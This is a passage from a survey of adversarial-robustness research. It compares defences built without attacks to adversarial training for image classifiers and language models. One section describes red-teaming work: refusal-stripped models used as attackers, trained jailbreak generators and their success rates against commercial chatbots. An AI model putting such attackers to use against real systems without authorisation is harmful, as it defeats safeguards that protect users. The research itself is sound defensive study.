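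The assumption of equal costs matters a great deal, and Raff and colleagues acknowledge that it is unrealistic. A bank can often recover money from an honest borrower whom its model approved by mistake, but not from a fraudster who has moved the money abroad. Unequal costs can change which model is the better choice. The AWP model has 88.25% clean accuracy and 60.5% accuracy under attack, while undefended CIFAR-10 models average 94.0% clean accuracy. Suppose that every attack on an undefended model succeeds and that 1% of inputs are attacks. Leaving training costs aside, AWP is then the better choice if a successful attack costs more than about nine times as much as an ordinary error. If only 0.1% of inputs are attacks, the threshold rises to about 95 times. Either ratio is plausible for fraud, but not for mislabelled holiday photographs.

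Raff and colleagues also judge how realistic different attacks are for an average company. They consider white-box attacks impractical, because an attacker with that much access usually has an easier way to do the same harm. Someone who can secretly alter a hospital's scans to change a diagnosis could alter the patient's record instead. They call an attack realistic only if it tries to fool a deployed model with partial or no knowledge of it. They base these ratings on their own judgement, not on measured frequencies.

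For most companies, Raff and colleagues recommend controls outside the model. A company can require a credit card or a security key for access, add hand-written rules, or retrain often enough that old attacks stop working. It can also check a random sample of predictions by hand, which limits how common undetected attacks can be. One of their eight case studies is a fraud against a Chinese government tax office. Criminals used stolen photographs and deepfakes to pass a face recognition check and issue $77 million in false invoices. Raff and colleagues would have required people to register in person and sign with a cryptographic key. In another case, researchers took apart the anti-virus product Cylance and found text that made its model treat malicious files as harmless. Raff and colleagues consider robust machine learning one of the only workable remedies in that case, because anyone could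 obtain the product and study it.

They make exceptions for governments, banks and companies whose models become part of other companies' software. They also expect the risk to grow, because as a company closes its easier security holes, its models will eventually become the easiest target. They therefore want every company to include robustness in its long-term plans.

Their argument supports leaving many models undefended and protecting the systems around them, but it gives little support to the anti-adversary layer. They think the most realistic attacker sends queries through a public interface and improves the attack one step at a time, and such an attacker can defeat the layer.

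### Attacks that nobody simulated

A developer who trains a model on simulated attacks may leave it weak against others. In *Defense That Attacks*, Awad, Mohamed and Gomaa (2025) trained 36 image models against attacks that change each pixel by up to 2 of the 255 brightness levels. One of them, a DenseNet121, correctly classified 63.5% of unaltered ImageNet pictures. Its accuracy fell to 33.3% under a 20-step PGD attack of the size used in training, and to 8.1% when the attacker could change each pixel by up to 5 levels. Part of the second drop is unavoidable, since larger changes make any attack easier. The same concern applies to language models trained only on readable attacks, and to released models, whose developers would have to guess how attackers will fine-tune them.

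A defence built without attacks can't overfit to them, as supporters of attacker-free defences point out, but that doesn't show that it resists any attack. Some of its settings, such as how much noise to add, also depend on assumptions about the attacker. Developers who simulate attacks can widen their coverage by letting the simulated attacker learn during training. *Chasing Moving Targets with Online Self-Play Reinforcement Learning for Safer Language Models* (2025) reports that a model trained this way was substantially more robust on 14 safety benchmarks than one trained on a fixed collection of attacks. The method, called Self-RedTeam, largely preserved the model's general reasoning and conversational abilities.

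### Hazards of building attackers

Training a language model against attacks requires something to write harmful prompts, and models with safety training often refuse. In *ADVERSA*, Owiredu-Ashley (2026) found that GPT-4 refused about 85% of requests to generate attacks. Researchers therefore use attackers without refusals. In *Safety Alignment of LMs via Non-cooperative Games*, Paulus, Kulikov and colleagues (2026) trained an attacker and a defender together, a method they call AdvGame. When Llama 3.1 refused to play the attacker, they replaced it with a public copy whose refusals someone had already removed. In *Reward Integrity in Adversarial Reinforcement Learning for LLM Guardrail Red-Teaming*, Liu, Kemik and colleagues (2026) at the Commonwealth Bank of Australia started from a similar "decensored" copy of OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b.

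Training then makes these models better at attacking. Paulus and colleagues describe their trained attacker as a "strong, general-purpose red-teaming agent" that people can use directly against arbitrary models. Red-teaming means attacking a system to find its weaknesses, normally with the owner's consent, but the attacker would work just as well without it. In their test, the attacker wrote ten prompts for each request in a standard set of harmful requests. At least one prompt succeeded for 55.6% of requests against the original Qwen2.5-7B and for 34.4% against the original Llama 3.1-8B. Three established attacks succeeded for 45.0% to 61.6% of requests on Qwen and 42.5% to 49.0% on Llama. The trained attacker was therefore roughly as good as existing methods on Qwen and somewhat worse on Llama, but it writes each prompt in a single pass, without a search. Qwen and Llama were also the starting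 points for the defenders in the same project, so these results are weak evidence of how the attacker would do against an unrelated system.

Owiredu-Ashley's attacker, built for testing rather than for training a defender, gives some evidence on that. He trained a 70-billion-parameter Llama model on 10,724 adversarial examples in about ten hours on one graphics processor. It then held 15 conversations with Claude Opus 4.6, Gemini 3.1 Pro and GPT-5.2, and succeeded in four, three times with its opening message. The sample is too small to rank the three systems, but an inexpensive attacker did work against commercial models whose weights he had never seen. Owiredu-Ashley withheld the attack prompts but lists the attacker model among the materials he released.

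Using one model as both attacker and defender, as in Self-RedTeam, creates a further hazard. Paulus and colleagues argue that a model able to write harmful attacks when prompted is necessarily unsafe as a defender, so they kept separate weights for the two roles.

The usual reply is that the same attackers are valuable for testing. In the bank's system, the attacker writes 12 attacks for each of four goals in every round, or 2,400 over 50 rounds, so the bank can look for weaknesses in its safeguards before a customer finds them. Tests are also more accurate when the attacker never refuses. In Owiredu-Ashley's study, the attacker still refused three times during conversations with Gemini, which made Gemini look more resistant than it may have been. But automated testing has its own errors. Liu and colleagues found that the model judging the results sometimes counted an attack as breaking a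 rule when it had not. Paulus and colleagues recommend that developers keep attack prompts and trained attackers in controlled settings, for authorised testing only.

Developers who train a defence without an attacker still need one to test whether it works, so leaving attacks out of training removes less of the hazard than it seems to. It does keep harmful examples out of the deployed model's training data, and occasional tests may need a less capable attacker than continuous training does. Anyone can already download models that don't refuse harmful requests, and leaving attacks out of training can't change that.

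### Robust models as sources of attacks

Adversarial training may also make other people's models less safe. Awad and colleagues tested whether adversarially trained models make better substitutes for building transfer attacks. They chose four small architectures from their set of 36 as substitutes and eight larger ones as targets, each in an adversarially trained and an ordinary version. To build the attacks, they changed 2,000 ImageNet pictures by up to 16 brightness levels, using a method that focuses on the pixels that most influence a prediction. The table gives the targets' average accuracy, so a lower number means a more successful attack.

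| Substitute model | Adversarially trained targets | Ordinary targets |
|---|---|---|
| Adversarially trained | 13.16% | 26.58% |
| Ordinary | 48.09% | 32.88% |

Attacks built on adversarially trained substitutes worked better against both ordinary and adversarially trained targets, so an attacker who could choose either substitute would always choose the adversarially trained one. These attacks left ordinary targets with 27% accuracy and adversarially trained targets with 13%, which means that adversarial training was worse than no defence in this test.

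Awad and colleagues suggest that robust models have more in common with one another. In their maps of which parts of a picture influenced the prediction, an adversarially trained model relied on an ostrich's head, body and legs, while an ordinary one relied more on feather texture and background. Many models use the shape of the animal, so an attack that disrupts it should transfer well. This explanation is plausible, but the maps only illustrate it and don't prove it.

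The attack was eight times as large as those the models had faced in training, which may explain part of the result. Fenaux and colleagues allowed changes of only 4 brightness levels on ImageNet and found the opposite for undefended targets. Their accuracy fell by 25 percentage points more when the attacker used an undefended substitute than when it used the best defended one. Defended substitutes did better against defended targets, but by only 1.7 points. Djilani and colleagues, also with 4 levels, found that robust substitutes raised attack success by 6.49 points on average. The success rate of one attack, BASES, rose from 1.26% to 12.55% against the most robust models. All three studies found that robust models make better substitutes against other robust models. Their results for undefended targets differ, and the reason is unclear because the studies used different attacks as well as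 different limits.

Attackers can exploit this only if they have a robust model's weights. Dozens of robust models are already public, so a company doesn't deprive attackers of anything by avoiding adversarial training, and it gives them nothing new if it trains a robust model and keeps it private. The finding is a better argument for caution about publishing robust models than for avoiding adversarial training.

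### Lost accuracy and needless refusals

Adversarial training lowers image classifiers' accuracy on ordinary pictures, and it can make language models more likely to refuse harmless requests. Paulus and colleagues measured how often their models answered harmless prompts before and after training against the attacker. On prompts from the WildJailbreak collection, Llama's rate fell from 98.8% to 69.9%, while Qwen's fell only from 100% to 94.4%. On XSTest, a set of harmless requests that sound dangerous, such as how to kill a Linux process, Llama's rate rose from 84.4% to 88.0%.

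Needless refusals are therefore a real drawback, but their number depends on the model and the test. General knowledge hardly changed, with Llama scoring 69.3% on the standard test MMLU before training and 69.1% after. Developers can also reward a model for answering harmless prompts during training. Paulus and colleagues did this, but Llama still did worse on WildJailbreak. Attacker-free defences can harm ordinary performance just as much. SND lowered the AWP model's clean accuracy by 18 points.

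### Which claims depend on results under attack

Four of the six claims are about effort and side effects: how easy the defence is to add, the hazards of building attackers, the help that robust models give to other attacks, and the loss of accuracy or helpfulness. These claims can be true of a defence that adds no worst-case protection, such as the anti-adversary layer. Low effort and few side effects are reasons to choose one working defence over another, but they can't make up for a lack of protection.

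The claims about attackers' limited access and about attacks that nobody simulated concern robustness, so they depend on how well a defence works under attack. The tests should include black-box attacks adapted to the defence if a developer expects only black-box attackers, and attacks the designers didn't have in mind if the defence is supposed to resist unforeseen ones.

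## How have other image defences built without attacks fared?

More than two dozen other image defences did well in their designers' tests but badly against attackers who knew how they worked. Masked gradients explain many of these failures, and the anti-adversary layer's too. Evaluators now have standard tools for getting past such masking.

### Getting past masked gradients

Athalye and colleagues distinguish three ways a defence can spoil gradients. It can include a step, such as rounding, that has no useful derivative. It can draw random numbers, so that the gradient is different on every run. Or it can pass the image through a long loop of computations, which can make the gradient shrink to almost nothing or grow too large to use.

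The remedy for the rounding problem is called backward pass differentiable approximation, or BPDA. Suppose a defence cleans each image with a step *g* before the classifier *f* sees it. The attacker runs the defended model exactly as it is, including the real *g*. When working backwards to get the gradient, the attacker replaces *g* with a smooth function that behaves similarly. A cleaning step should leave an image looking much the same, so the simplest replacement is a function that does nothing:

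$$\nabla_x f(g(x))\;\approx\;\nabla_z f(z)\Big|_{z=g(x)}$$

For example, if *g* rounds a brightness of 0.47 to 0.5, its true derivative there is zero. BPDA treats the derivative as 1, so the attacker finds the direction that raises the loss at 0.5 and moves the original 0.47 that way. Each step is slightly wrong, but over many steps the attack still makes progress. Athalye and colleagues found that the attacker has to keep the real *g* in the forward run, because replacing it there too made the attack much weaker or useless. The approximation also needs *g*(*x*) to be close to *x*. The anti-adversary layer can move a pixel by 76 brightness levels, so the approximation suits it badly.

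For random defences, attackers use expectation over transformation, or EOT. If the defence applies a random change *t* to each image, the attacker averages the gradient over *n* draws:

$$\nabla_x\,\mathbb{E}_t\big[f(t(x))\big]=\mathbb{E}_t\big[\nabla_x f(t(x))\big]\approx\frac{1}{n}\sum_{i=1}^{n}\nabla_x f(t_i(x))$$

The random error falls with the square root of *n*, so 100 draws reduce it to a tenth but take 100 times the computation.

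When a defence runs the image through a long loop, Athalye and colleagues search only among images that the loop would leave unchanged, so they can leave the loop out of the gradient calculation. An attacker can also avoid using the defended model's gradients by attacking the base model and transferring the resulting images to the defended one, or by using only the defended model's predicted labels, as RayS does.

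### The defences of 2018, 2020 and 2022

Athalye and colleagues tested nine defences that ICLR, a leading machine-learning conference, had accepted for 2018. Each was presented as resistant to white-box attackers, but none came with a proof. Seven relied on spoiled gradients. Attacks reduced four of these to 0% accuracy and two others to 5% and 9%. The seventh, Defense-GAN, kept 55% accuracy on handwritten digits. Athalye and colleagues argue that its principle gives no protection, and that only imperfections in its image generator stopped the theoretically best attack.

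The two defences that did not rely on spoiled gradients both used adversarial training. Mądry and colleagues' method kept 47% accuracy under attack, close to what its designers had reported. Cascade adversarial training kept 15%, against changes to the images that were half as large.

According to Tramèr and colleagues, almost no defence papers included adaptive attacks in 2017, a third did in 2018, and nearly all did by 2020. But when they attacked thirteen recent defences from the main conferences with existing techniques, they substantially reduced the accuracy of every one, and most turned out to add no robustness. One of the thirteen was a form of adversarial training, so not all of them were built without attacks.

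One of the thirteen, k-Winners-Take-All, masks gradients on purpose. In each layer, it keeps the *k* largest values and sets the rest to zero. A tiny change to the image can change which values are kept, so the output can change abruptly and the gradient gives little information about nearby images. Tramèr and colleagues found that in such cases a black-box attack sometimes works better than a gradient attack, even when the attacker has full access to the model.

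Many of the designers had made a different mistake in their own adaptive attacks. They had maximised a loss that did not track whether the attack succeeded, so even a perfect search would have missed the images that fool the model. Others had reused an attack that broke an earlier defence without adapting it to the new one.

In 2022, Croce and colleagues examined nine defences that do extra optimisation on every input, either to clean the image or adjust the model. The table gives accuracy on CIFAR-10 with changes of up to 8 brightness levels, or up to 2 for the defence marked with an asterisk.

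| Defence | Claimed | Measured | Base model alone |
|---|---|---|---|
| Layer that solves a differential equation | 57.8% | 52.2% | 53.9% |
| Raising the loss on all classes at once | 65.7% | 61.0% | 63.0% |
| Anti-adversary layer | 79.2% | 66.6% | 66.6% |
| Cleaning guided by an attack detector | 52.7% | 43.8% | 49.3% |
| Cleaning guided by image comparisons | 63.8% | 58.4% | 59.4% |
| Correcting the network's inner values* | 50% | 5.6% | 0.0% |
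| Cleaning guided by a self-supervised task | 51.0% | 3.7% | 0.0% |
| Cleaning in a single step | 65.1% | 12.6% | 7.7% |
| Cleaning with a score-based generative model | 69.7% | 33.7% | 0.0% |

The first five defences were added to base models that adversarial training had already made robust, and none improved on its base model. The other four started from models with little or no robustness. Three of these gained between 4 and 6 percentage points, and the last gained 33.7. The defence with an attack detector is not attacker-free, because its designers trained the detector on attacked images. It still lowered the base model's accuracy by 5.5 points.

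Some of the inflated claims came from a detail of the AutoAttack software. AutoAttack returns the original image when its attack fails or when the model already misclassifies the image. This is harmless when the tester attacks a model directly, but several designers ran AutoAttack on a robust base model and tested the defended model on the results, so most of the "attacked" images were unaltered. The differential-equation defence scored 60.9% accuracy on this test. Its accuracy fell to 52.2% on images altered to raise the base model's loss as far as possible, whether or not they fooled the base model.

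The defence that corrects inner values was presented as infeasible to attack adaptively, on the grounds that the gradient of its optimisation was too hard to compute. Croce and colleagues ignored most of the optimisation and used only the gradient of the final run. In their reproduction of the defence, this reduced accuracy from 34.5% to 9.5%, and a better search reduced it to 5.6%.

Attacking the self-supervised defence required a more careful approximation of the gradient. The defence's cleaning produces a series of intermediate images, and the simplest form of BPDA uses the gradient at only the last one. Croce and colleagues averaged the gradients over the whole series, so that the attack pushed every intermediate image towards a wrong label. This reduced accuracy to 3.7%.

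### Diffusion purification

The only large gain in the table comes from purification, a family of defences that try to replace a suspicious image with a natural one that looks like it. Two of the 2018 defences, PixelDefend and Defense-GAN, already did this with older image generators. The best-known later version, DiffPure (Nie et al., 2022), uses a diffusion model, a generator that learns to turn noise into pictures by removing a little noise at a time.

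DiffPure cleans an image *x* as follows:

1. Mix the image with random noise. For a chosen amount of noise *t*, the result is

$$x_t=\sqrt{\bar\alpha_t}\,x+\sqrt{1-\bar\alpha_t}\;\epsilon$$

where ε is Gaussian noise and ᾱ, a number between 0 and 1, falls as *t* grows.

2. Run the diffusion model backwards from *x*ₜ, removing noise step by step until a clean picture remains.
3. Give that picture to the ordinary classifier.

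The defence adds noise to the image to mask the attacker's changes, then uses a diffusion model to fill in what a natural image would contain. There must be enough noise to hide the changes, but not so much that the object in the picture disappears. The diffusion model learns from ordinary pictures and random noise, so training it doesn't require a simulated attacker, and its designers expected the defence to work against unforeseen attacks.

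DiffPure's published results were strong. *ZeroPur* (Liu, Yang and colleagues, 2024) lists its accuracy under AutoAttack as 70.64% on CIFAR-10 and 40.93% on ImageNet. Its clean accuracy on CIFAR-10 was 89.02%. The adversarially trained CIFAR-10 models of the same architecture in that comparison kept between 60.7% and 63.9% under attack.

These figures depend on how well the attack handled a difficult calculation. Removing the noise takes many consecutive runs of a large network, each involving randomness. To get an exact gradient, an attacker has to trace the calculation back through every run, which takes a lot of memory, and the gradient may vanish or explode on the way. *Test-Time Adversarial Defense with Opposite Adversarial Path and High Attack Time Cost* (Yeh, Yu and Lu, 2025) describes two later attacks that deal with this. Lee and Kim (2023) computed gradients through a substitute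 process with fewer steps. Under their attack, DiffPure kept about 47% to 51% accuracy on CIFAR-10, depending on the classifier, and they concluded that earlier tests had overstated the robustness of diffusion purifiers. DiffAttack, from Kang and colleagues, divides the sequence of runs into segments so that the attacker can trace the calculation much further.

The score-based purifier in the table suggests how large the overstatement can be. It is closely related to DiffPure. It adds noise to the image, removes it in ten steps, and repeats the process ten times. Its designers tested it with BPDA and EOT and reported 69.7% robust accuracy. But the purifier consists entirely of ordinary network runs, so its exact gradient is available and BPDA only makes the attack less accurate. Croce and colleagues used the exact gradient, averaged over 200 random draws at each of ten steps, and measured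 33.7%. The base model had 0%, so purification did make it harder to attack, though any stronger attack would lower the figure. Purification also made inference take 176 times as long.

Yeh and colleagues draw a different lesson from the difficulty of these attacks. They want adaptive attacks to require as much computation as possible, and add a second diffusion path to their purifier partly for that reason. This can deter an attacker with limited computing power. But the defender has to run the extra computation on every image, while the attacker runs it only for the images worth attacking.

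Their purifier also shows that training on attacked images is not enough by itself to make a defence robust. They trained it to move each attacked image past the original picture and further into the region of the right label. The best versions kept 86.1% and 88.8% accuracy against attacks that did not account for the purifier, but at most 59.9% under BPDA. The three tests used different classifiers, so the gap is only a rough guide to BPDA's effect.

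ZeroPur needs no generator or training. It repeatedly adjusts an image so that its features inside the classifier move closer to those of a blurred copy, then pushes it further in the same direction. Liu and colleagues report 69.6% accuracy on CIFAR-10 and 67.1% on ImageNet under a version of AutoAttack for randomised defences. Their listed tests also include BPDA and another attack designed to survive blurring.

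Several of the AutoAttack results cannot be close to the true robust accuracy. With only the first stage of ZeroPur, one CIFAR-10 model classified 49.6% of ordinary images correctly and 58.8% of attacked ones. An attacker can always submit the ordinary image unchanged, so true robust accuracy cannot exceed clean accuracy, which was 49.6% here. On ImageNet, blurring each picture appeared to give 60.4% robust accuracy, far above the 40.6% of the best adversarially trained model in the comparison. A blur has a usable gradient, so the attack most likely did not take the blur into account.

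Such comparisons also include outdated figures. Liu and colleagues list the self-supervised defence at 66.6% and 68.6%, and the score-based purifier at 59.5%. Two years earlier, Croce and colleagues had measured 3.7% for the self-supervised defence and 33.7% for the purifier. The networks may differ, but not by enough to explain the self-supervised defence's 60-point gap.

### A purifier that models the adversary

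Generic purification treats an attack as one more kind of damage to an image, like blur or static. Wesego and Rooshenas (2025), in *Adversary Aware Optimization for Robust Defense*, instead build an assumption about the attacker into the cleaning. In Bayesian terms, a purifier that receives an image *x*′ looks for the clean image *x* that maximises

$$\log p(x)+\log p(x'\mid x)$$

The first term measures how natural *x* looks, and Wesego and Rooshenas take it from a pretrained diffusion model. The second measures how likely someone would be to turn *x* into *x*′. In a generic purifier, this term might describe random noise, but they tailor it to adversarial changes.

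The difference could matter, because attacks don't look like random noise. The fast gradient sign method, for example, moves every pixel by exactly the permitted amount, which random noise would almost never do. The defence is still attacker-free if the second term describes only the size and shape of the permitted changes, but not if its designers fitted that term to attacks that had succeeded.

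Wesego and Rooshenas report high robust accuracy on CIFAR-10 and CIFAR-100 against a range of common attacks. Most of the defences in the table above also did well against common attacks. This purifier also optimises each image at run time, so the deciding tests would be attacks that follow the gradient through that optimisation and attacks transferred from the undefended classifier.

### Ensemble everything everywhere

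The most promising attacker-free defence of 2024 was inspired by the eye. Fort and Lakshminarayanan (2024) argued in *Ensemble everything everywhere* that people see an object as a stream of shifting, partly blurred views, while a classifier gets a single sharp picture. Their defence has three parts.

The first part gives the network copies of each image at several resolutions. For CIFAR images, which are 32 pixels wide, it makes copies at widths of 32, 16, 8 and 4 pixels, adds noise and small random shifts to each, and stacks them into one input. The second part takes predictions from layers throughout the network. Fort and Lakshminarayanan had noticed that when an attack changes the last layer's prediction from "dog" to "car", the predictions from earlier layers are still mostly "dog".

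The third part, called CrossMax, combines these predictions so that no single layer can dominate. It subtracts each layer's highest score from all of that layer's scores, then subtracts each class's highest remaining score from that class's scores, and finally takes a middle or *k*th-highest value for each class. Suppose that three layers score a picture of a cat and an attacker has fooled one of them:

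| | Cat | Dog | Car |
|---|---|---|---|
| Layer A | 4 | 2 | 1 |
| Layer B | 5 | 1 | 1 |
| Layer C (fooled) | 2 | 1 | 20 |
| Average | 3.7 | 1.3 | 7.3 |
| CrossMax, middle value | 0 | −2 | −3 |

A plain average would choose "car", but CrossMax chooses "cat". If the attacker raises layer C's score for "car" from 20 to 30, CrossMax's result doesn't change. This makes the vote harder to manipulate, but it also makes the gradient with respect to that score zero.

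Fort and Lakshminarayanan reported accuracy under AutoAttack of about 72% on CIFAR-10 and 48% on CIFAR-100, without adversarial training. They argued that the figures were real because when they altered an image to make the model assign it to a chosen class, the result looked like that class to a person. They proposed that a model will be robust if attacks on it look meaningful to people.

The first re-evaluation, in November 2024, reported almost no robustness, but it contained a serious error. Zhang, Nikolić, Carlini and Tramèr ran their attack in up to 20 rounds, and each round measured the permitted change from the previous round's output instead of from the original image. Fort (2025) reproduced the error in *A Note on Implementation Errors in Recent Adaptive Attacks Against Multi-Resolution Self-Ensembles*. The total change was 8 brightness levels after one round, about 16 after two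 and about 31 after four, and it could reach 160. Zhang and colleagues acknowledged the mistake.

They then worked with a second group that had been testing the same defence, and together published a corrected study, *Evaluating the Robustness of the "Ensemble Everything Everywhere" Defense* (Zhang, Schlarmann and colleagues, 2024). They trained the defence with its public code and checked whether AutoAttack was reliable on it. Their models were somewhat less accurate on CIFAR-10 than the larger ones in the original paper.

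Researchers tested the original attack code by retraining the model's last layer so that every image was certain to have a successful attack nearby. The code found only 60% of these attacks. They also plotted the loss around an image and found it full of spikes. Holding the random numbers fixed made the surface much smoother, so randomness was causing most of the spikes.

Their own attack used only existing techniques. In the main step, they replaced CrossMax with a plain average, attacked that version, and used the resulting images against the real defence. The table shows accuracy as they added each part, with image changes limited to 8 brightness levels throughout.

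| Attack | CIFAR-10 | CIFAR-100 |
|---|---|---|
| None | 88.9% | 64.1% |
| AutoAttack | 61.8% | 47.9% |
| PGD with 500 steps | 54.0% | 34.6% |
| Transfer from the version with a plain average | 32.6% | 22.2% |
| Averaging over randomness (EOT) | 27.5% | 19.5% |
| More steps, more draws and a different loss | 11.3% | 13.8% |
| Best of this and a second attack | 10.9% | 13.6% |

These figures come from 100 images and ten runs each, so they are uncertain by a few points, but the drop is much larger than that.

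In his earlier note on the faulty first version, Fort had reported that a stronger model using all 54 layers kept more than 20% accuracy on CIFAR-100 in a preliminary test with a properly limited attack. The two results can both be right, because the models differ and each figure is an upper bound. Even 20% is less than half the accuracy originally claimed.

He also questioned whether all of the successful attacks should count, since the model has not made a mistake if an attack changes what a picture shows. At a lecture, he showed the audience two attacked images and a short list of classes, and they mostly agreed with the model that a house was a road and that the sea was a mountain. But two small pictures and a short list of answers are weak evidence, and Zhang and colleagues found that only some of their changes looked meaningful. The best adversarially trained models of the time kept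 about 42% accuracy on CIFAR-100 under the same limit, so changes of meaning can't account for most of the fall to 14%.

Attacks on ME-Net, one of the thirteen defences from 2020, also looked meaningful, but the defence turned out to have little robustness. This counts against treating meaningful-looking attacks as a sign of robustness. Interpretable gradients are common in robust models but don't guarantee robustness.

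### Two claims from 2026

In *Reinforcement Learning Disrupts Gradient-Based Adversarial Optimization*, Zou, Zhao and colleagues (2026) trained image classifiers by trial and error. The network guesses a label, gets a reward of 1 if the guess is right, and makes half its guesses at random to encourage exploration. On CIFAR-10, this raised accuracy under PGD attack from 5% to 56% and lowered clean accuracy by about 2 points.

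The attack allowed very large changes, equivalent to moving every pixel value by about 32 brightness levels, which makes the 56% accuracy more suspicious. In tests by Zou and colleagues, images built on an ordinarily trained network reduced the new model's accuracy to 8%. When they ran AutoAttack's main gradient attack separately, the model kept 16.7% accuracy, compared with 15.4% for ordinary training. Under the black-box Square Attack, the figures were 12.0% and 11.6%. The researchers conclude that their method disrupts the search for harmful inputs but does not remove them, which is known as gradient masking.

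They therefore recommend combining reinforcement learning with adversarial training. The combination kept 32.4% accuracy under Square Attack, compared with 19.6% for adversarial training alone, and 30.9% against images transferred from the ordinary network, compared with 9.5%. The transfer result is more convincing because it doesn't use the defended model's gradients. But both models were trained against the weak one-step attack, and stronger adversarial training might close the gap. Reinforcement learning also ran for 2,000 passes through the data, compared with 100 for ordinary training.

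The other claim concerns services that return a score for every class. In *Mitigating Black-Box Score-Based Query Attacks via Gradient Confusion*, Javeri, Hezareh and colleagues (2026) alter those scores so that gradients estimated from them lead an attacker in the wrong direction. The defence keeps the top label and limits how far the scores may move. On CIFAR-10, with a limit of 1,000 queries per image, it reduced the success rate of one version of Square Attack from 99.4% to 30.7% without reducing accuracy.

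Javeri and colleagues tested their defence against four score-based attacks and two adaptive variants of Square Attack. One variant used expectation over transformation (EOT), averaging ten answers to cancel out randomness. The defence is deterministic, so all ten answers are the same and the averaging only wastes queries. The other variant reversed direction when progress stalled and succeeded on 30.1% of ImageNet images.

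The defence's main tests included neither transfer attacks nor attacks that use only labels. The argument about the anti-adversary layer applies even more strictly here, because this defence corrects its scores whenever the top label would change. RayS would receive the same answers with or without the defence, and it can succeed well within the limit of 1,000 queries. The defence may slow attackers who rely on scores, but a service could get the same protection against them by returning no scores.

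### What leads the benchmarks

RobustBench, a public leaderboard for image models, ranks entries by their accuracy under AutoAttack. Its rules in 2022 excluded models that have zero gradients, use randomness or optimise during inference, because AutoAttack is unreliable on such models. DiffPure, "Ensemble everything everywhere" and the anti-adversary layer each meet at least one of these criteria, so their absence from the ranking is not evidence against them. Croce and colleagues worry that such rules could hold back useful research.

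Adversarially trained models topped the leaderboard when Fort and Lakshminarayanan compared their results with it in August 2024. The improvements they claimed imply that the leaders' accuracy under attack was about 73% on CIFAR-10 and 42% to 43% on CIFAR-100. Three defences built without attacks, on ordinary base models, were less accurate under adaptive attack: DiffPure scored about 47% to 51% on CIFAR-10, the score-based purifier 33.7%, and "Ensemble everything everywhere" just over 20% on CIFAR-100 in Fort's preliminary test. Besides adversarial training, Zhang and colleagues name only two approaches that have lasted, certified defences and randomised smoothing, which both offer guarantees rather than a record against known attacks.

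## What can be proved about defences that never see an attack?

Tests give only an upper bound on a defence's robust accuracy, but a proof can give a lower bound. Proofs can also show why ordinary training produces fragile models and how much a developer can guarantee without knowing what the attacker will try.

### Why ordinary training leaves a model exposed

Frei, Vardi and colleagues (2023) prove in *The Double-Edged Sword of Implicit Bias* that, for one kind of data, ordinary training produces a fragile network even though a robust one exists. The fragility in that case therefore can't be explained by the lack of a robust network for the task.

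Their data form *k* clusters in a space of *d* dimensions. The centre of each cluster is √*d* from the origin, and the points scatter around it with Gaussian (bell-curve) noise. All points in a cluster share a positive or negative label. The centres lie in nearly perpendicular directions, so the distance between clusters also grows in proportion to √*d*. This leaves room for a boundary far from every cluster. If clusters with opposite labels nearly touched, no classifier could be robust.

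The network has two layers. Each unit in the first layer outputs a weighted sum of the input, or zero if that sum is negative. The second layer takes a weighted sum of these outputs, and its sign is the predicted label. Training follows gradient flow, an idealised form of gradient descent with infinitely small steps.

Frei and colleagues build the robust network by hand, with one unit per cluster that responds only to points in that cluster. An attacker has to move a typical input by more than √*d*/8 to change its label. Gradient flow instead makes the weights converge, once the training loss is low enough, towards a network that classifies new points well but changes its label for almost all of them under a shift proportional to √(*d*/*k*). This shift gets smaller relative to the distance between clusters as the number of clusters grows.

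A linear classifier shows why. Suppose there are 10,000 dimensions and 100 clusters with exactly perpendicular centres, each at a distance of 100 from the origin. The classifier adds up evidence from all the clusters, scoring 1 at every positive centre and −1 at every negative one. An attacker starts at a positive centre and takes 100 steps of length 1: one in the direction of each negative centre from the origin, and one opposite to the direction of each positive centre. Each step lowers the score by 0.01, so together they lower it from 1 to the boundary at 0. But because the steps are perpendicular, the total distance is only 10. Random noise of the same length would typically change the score by only about 0.01. In the hand-built network, only one of these directions affects the active unit, and the attacker has to move the same point by 50 to turn that unit off.

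This is the same accumulation of small effects that Goodfellow and colleagues described for pixels. The trained network isn't linear, but Frei and colleagues prove that it remains sensitive to all *k* directions at once. Apart from its sign, the harmful shift is the same for every input, and it works on every network that gradient flow could converge to. The theorem therefore reproduces the familiar observations that one pattern can fool a model on many images and that attacks transfer between models. Making the network wider or starting from different weights doesn't remove the problem.

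The result covers only two-layer networks and data that a flat boundary can separate, although Frei and colleagues conjecture that it extends to many more clusters. It also covers only ordinary training, so it is not evidence against attacker-free defences in general. The hand-built network is constructed from the clusters' positions, without using any attacks. If the clusters are tight, even a nearest-neighbour classifier, which gives each input the label of the closest training example, is robust on this data.

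### Learning when the permitted changes are unknown

In that setting, the attacker may move an input a short distance, which is easy to define. Many developers would rather have protection against any change that a person wouldn't notice, but nobody can specify those changes exactly. *Adversarially Robust Learning with Unknown Perturbation Sets* (Montasser, Hanneke and Srebro, 2021) studies what a learner can guarantee without a description of the permitted changes.

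Their learner has ordinary labelled examples and access to an *attack oracle*, an idealised attacker. The learner submits a classifier and an example, and the oracle either returns a permitted change that makes the classifier fail or confirms that there is none. Every attack it returns is an attacker signal. The simplest algorithm is an idealised form of adversarial training:

1. Submit the current classifier to the oracle with each training example in turn.
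2. If the oracle returns an attack, update the classifier on the attacked example, using the correct label.
3. Stop after a full pass in which the oracle finds nothing.

The updates come from an online learner, an algorithm that takes examples one at a time and updates its classifier after each mistake. For some classes of classifier, if at least one classifier in the class fits every example, the best online learner makes at most a fixed number of mistakes, called the Littlestone dimension, whatever the examples are. Each attack the oracle returns is a mistake by the learner, so the Littlestone dimension also limits the number of attacks, and the loop must end. With enough training examples, the final classifier is robust on new examples too.

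Montasser and colleagues also prove a converse. If a class has no finite Littlestone dimension, no learner can guarantee robustness with a fixed number of calls to the oracle. One example is the class of thresholds, classifiers that check whether a number lies below some cut-off. Thresholds are about the easiest class to learn in the ordinary sense, but with *n* possible cut-offs, the learner needs a number of oracle calls that grows with the logarithm of *n*. For 1,024 cut-offs the minimum from the proof is about five, and for infinitely many no fixed number is enough. In the proof, one set of changes is picked at random from a long list of possible sets. The learner has to find out which one was picked, and clean data don't help, even if it knows their distribution perfectly.

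This counts against the claim that attacker-free defences are ready for attacks nobody foresaw. A developer who neither knows the permitted changes nor sees any attacks cannot guarantee robustness in general, however much clean data they collect. Particular defences may still happen to resist particular attacks.

In 2019, the same researchers showed that a learner with an explicit description of the permitted changes can robustly learn any class that is learnable in the ordinary sense, including thresholds. Such a description therefore helps a learner more than even a perfect attacker does. But the learner may work out the worst changes for itself from the description, which is hard to distinguish from searching for attacks.

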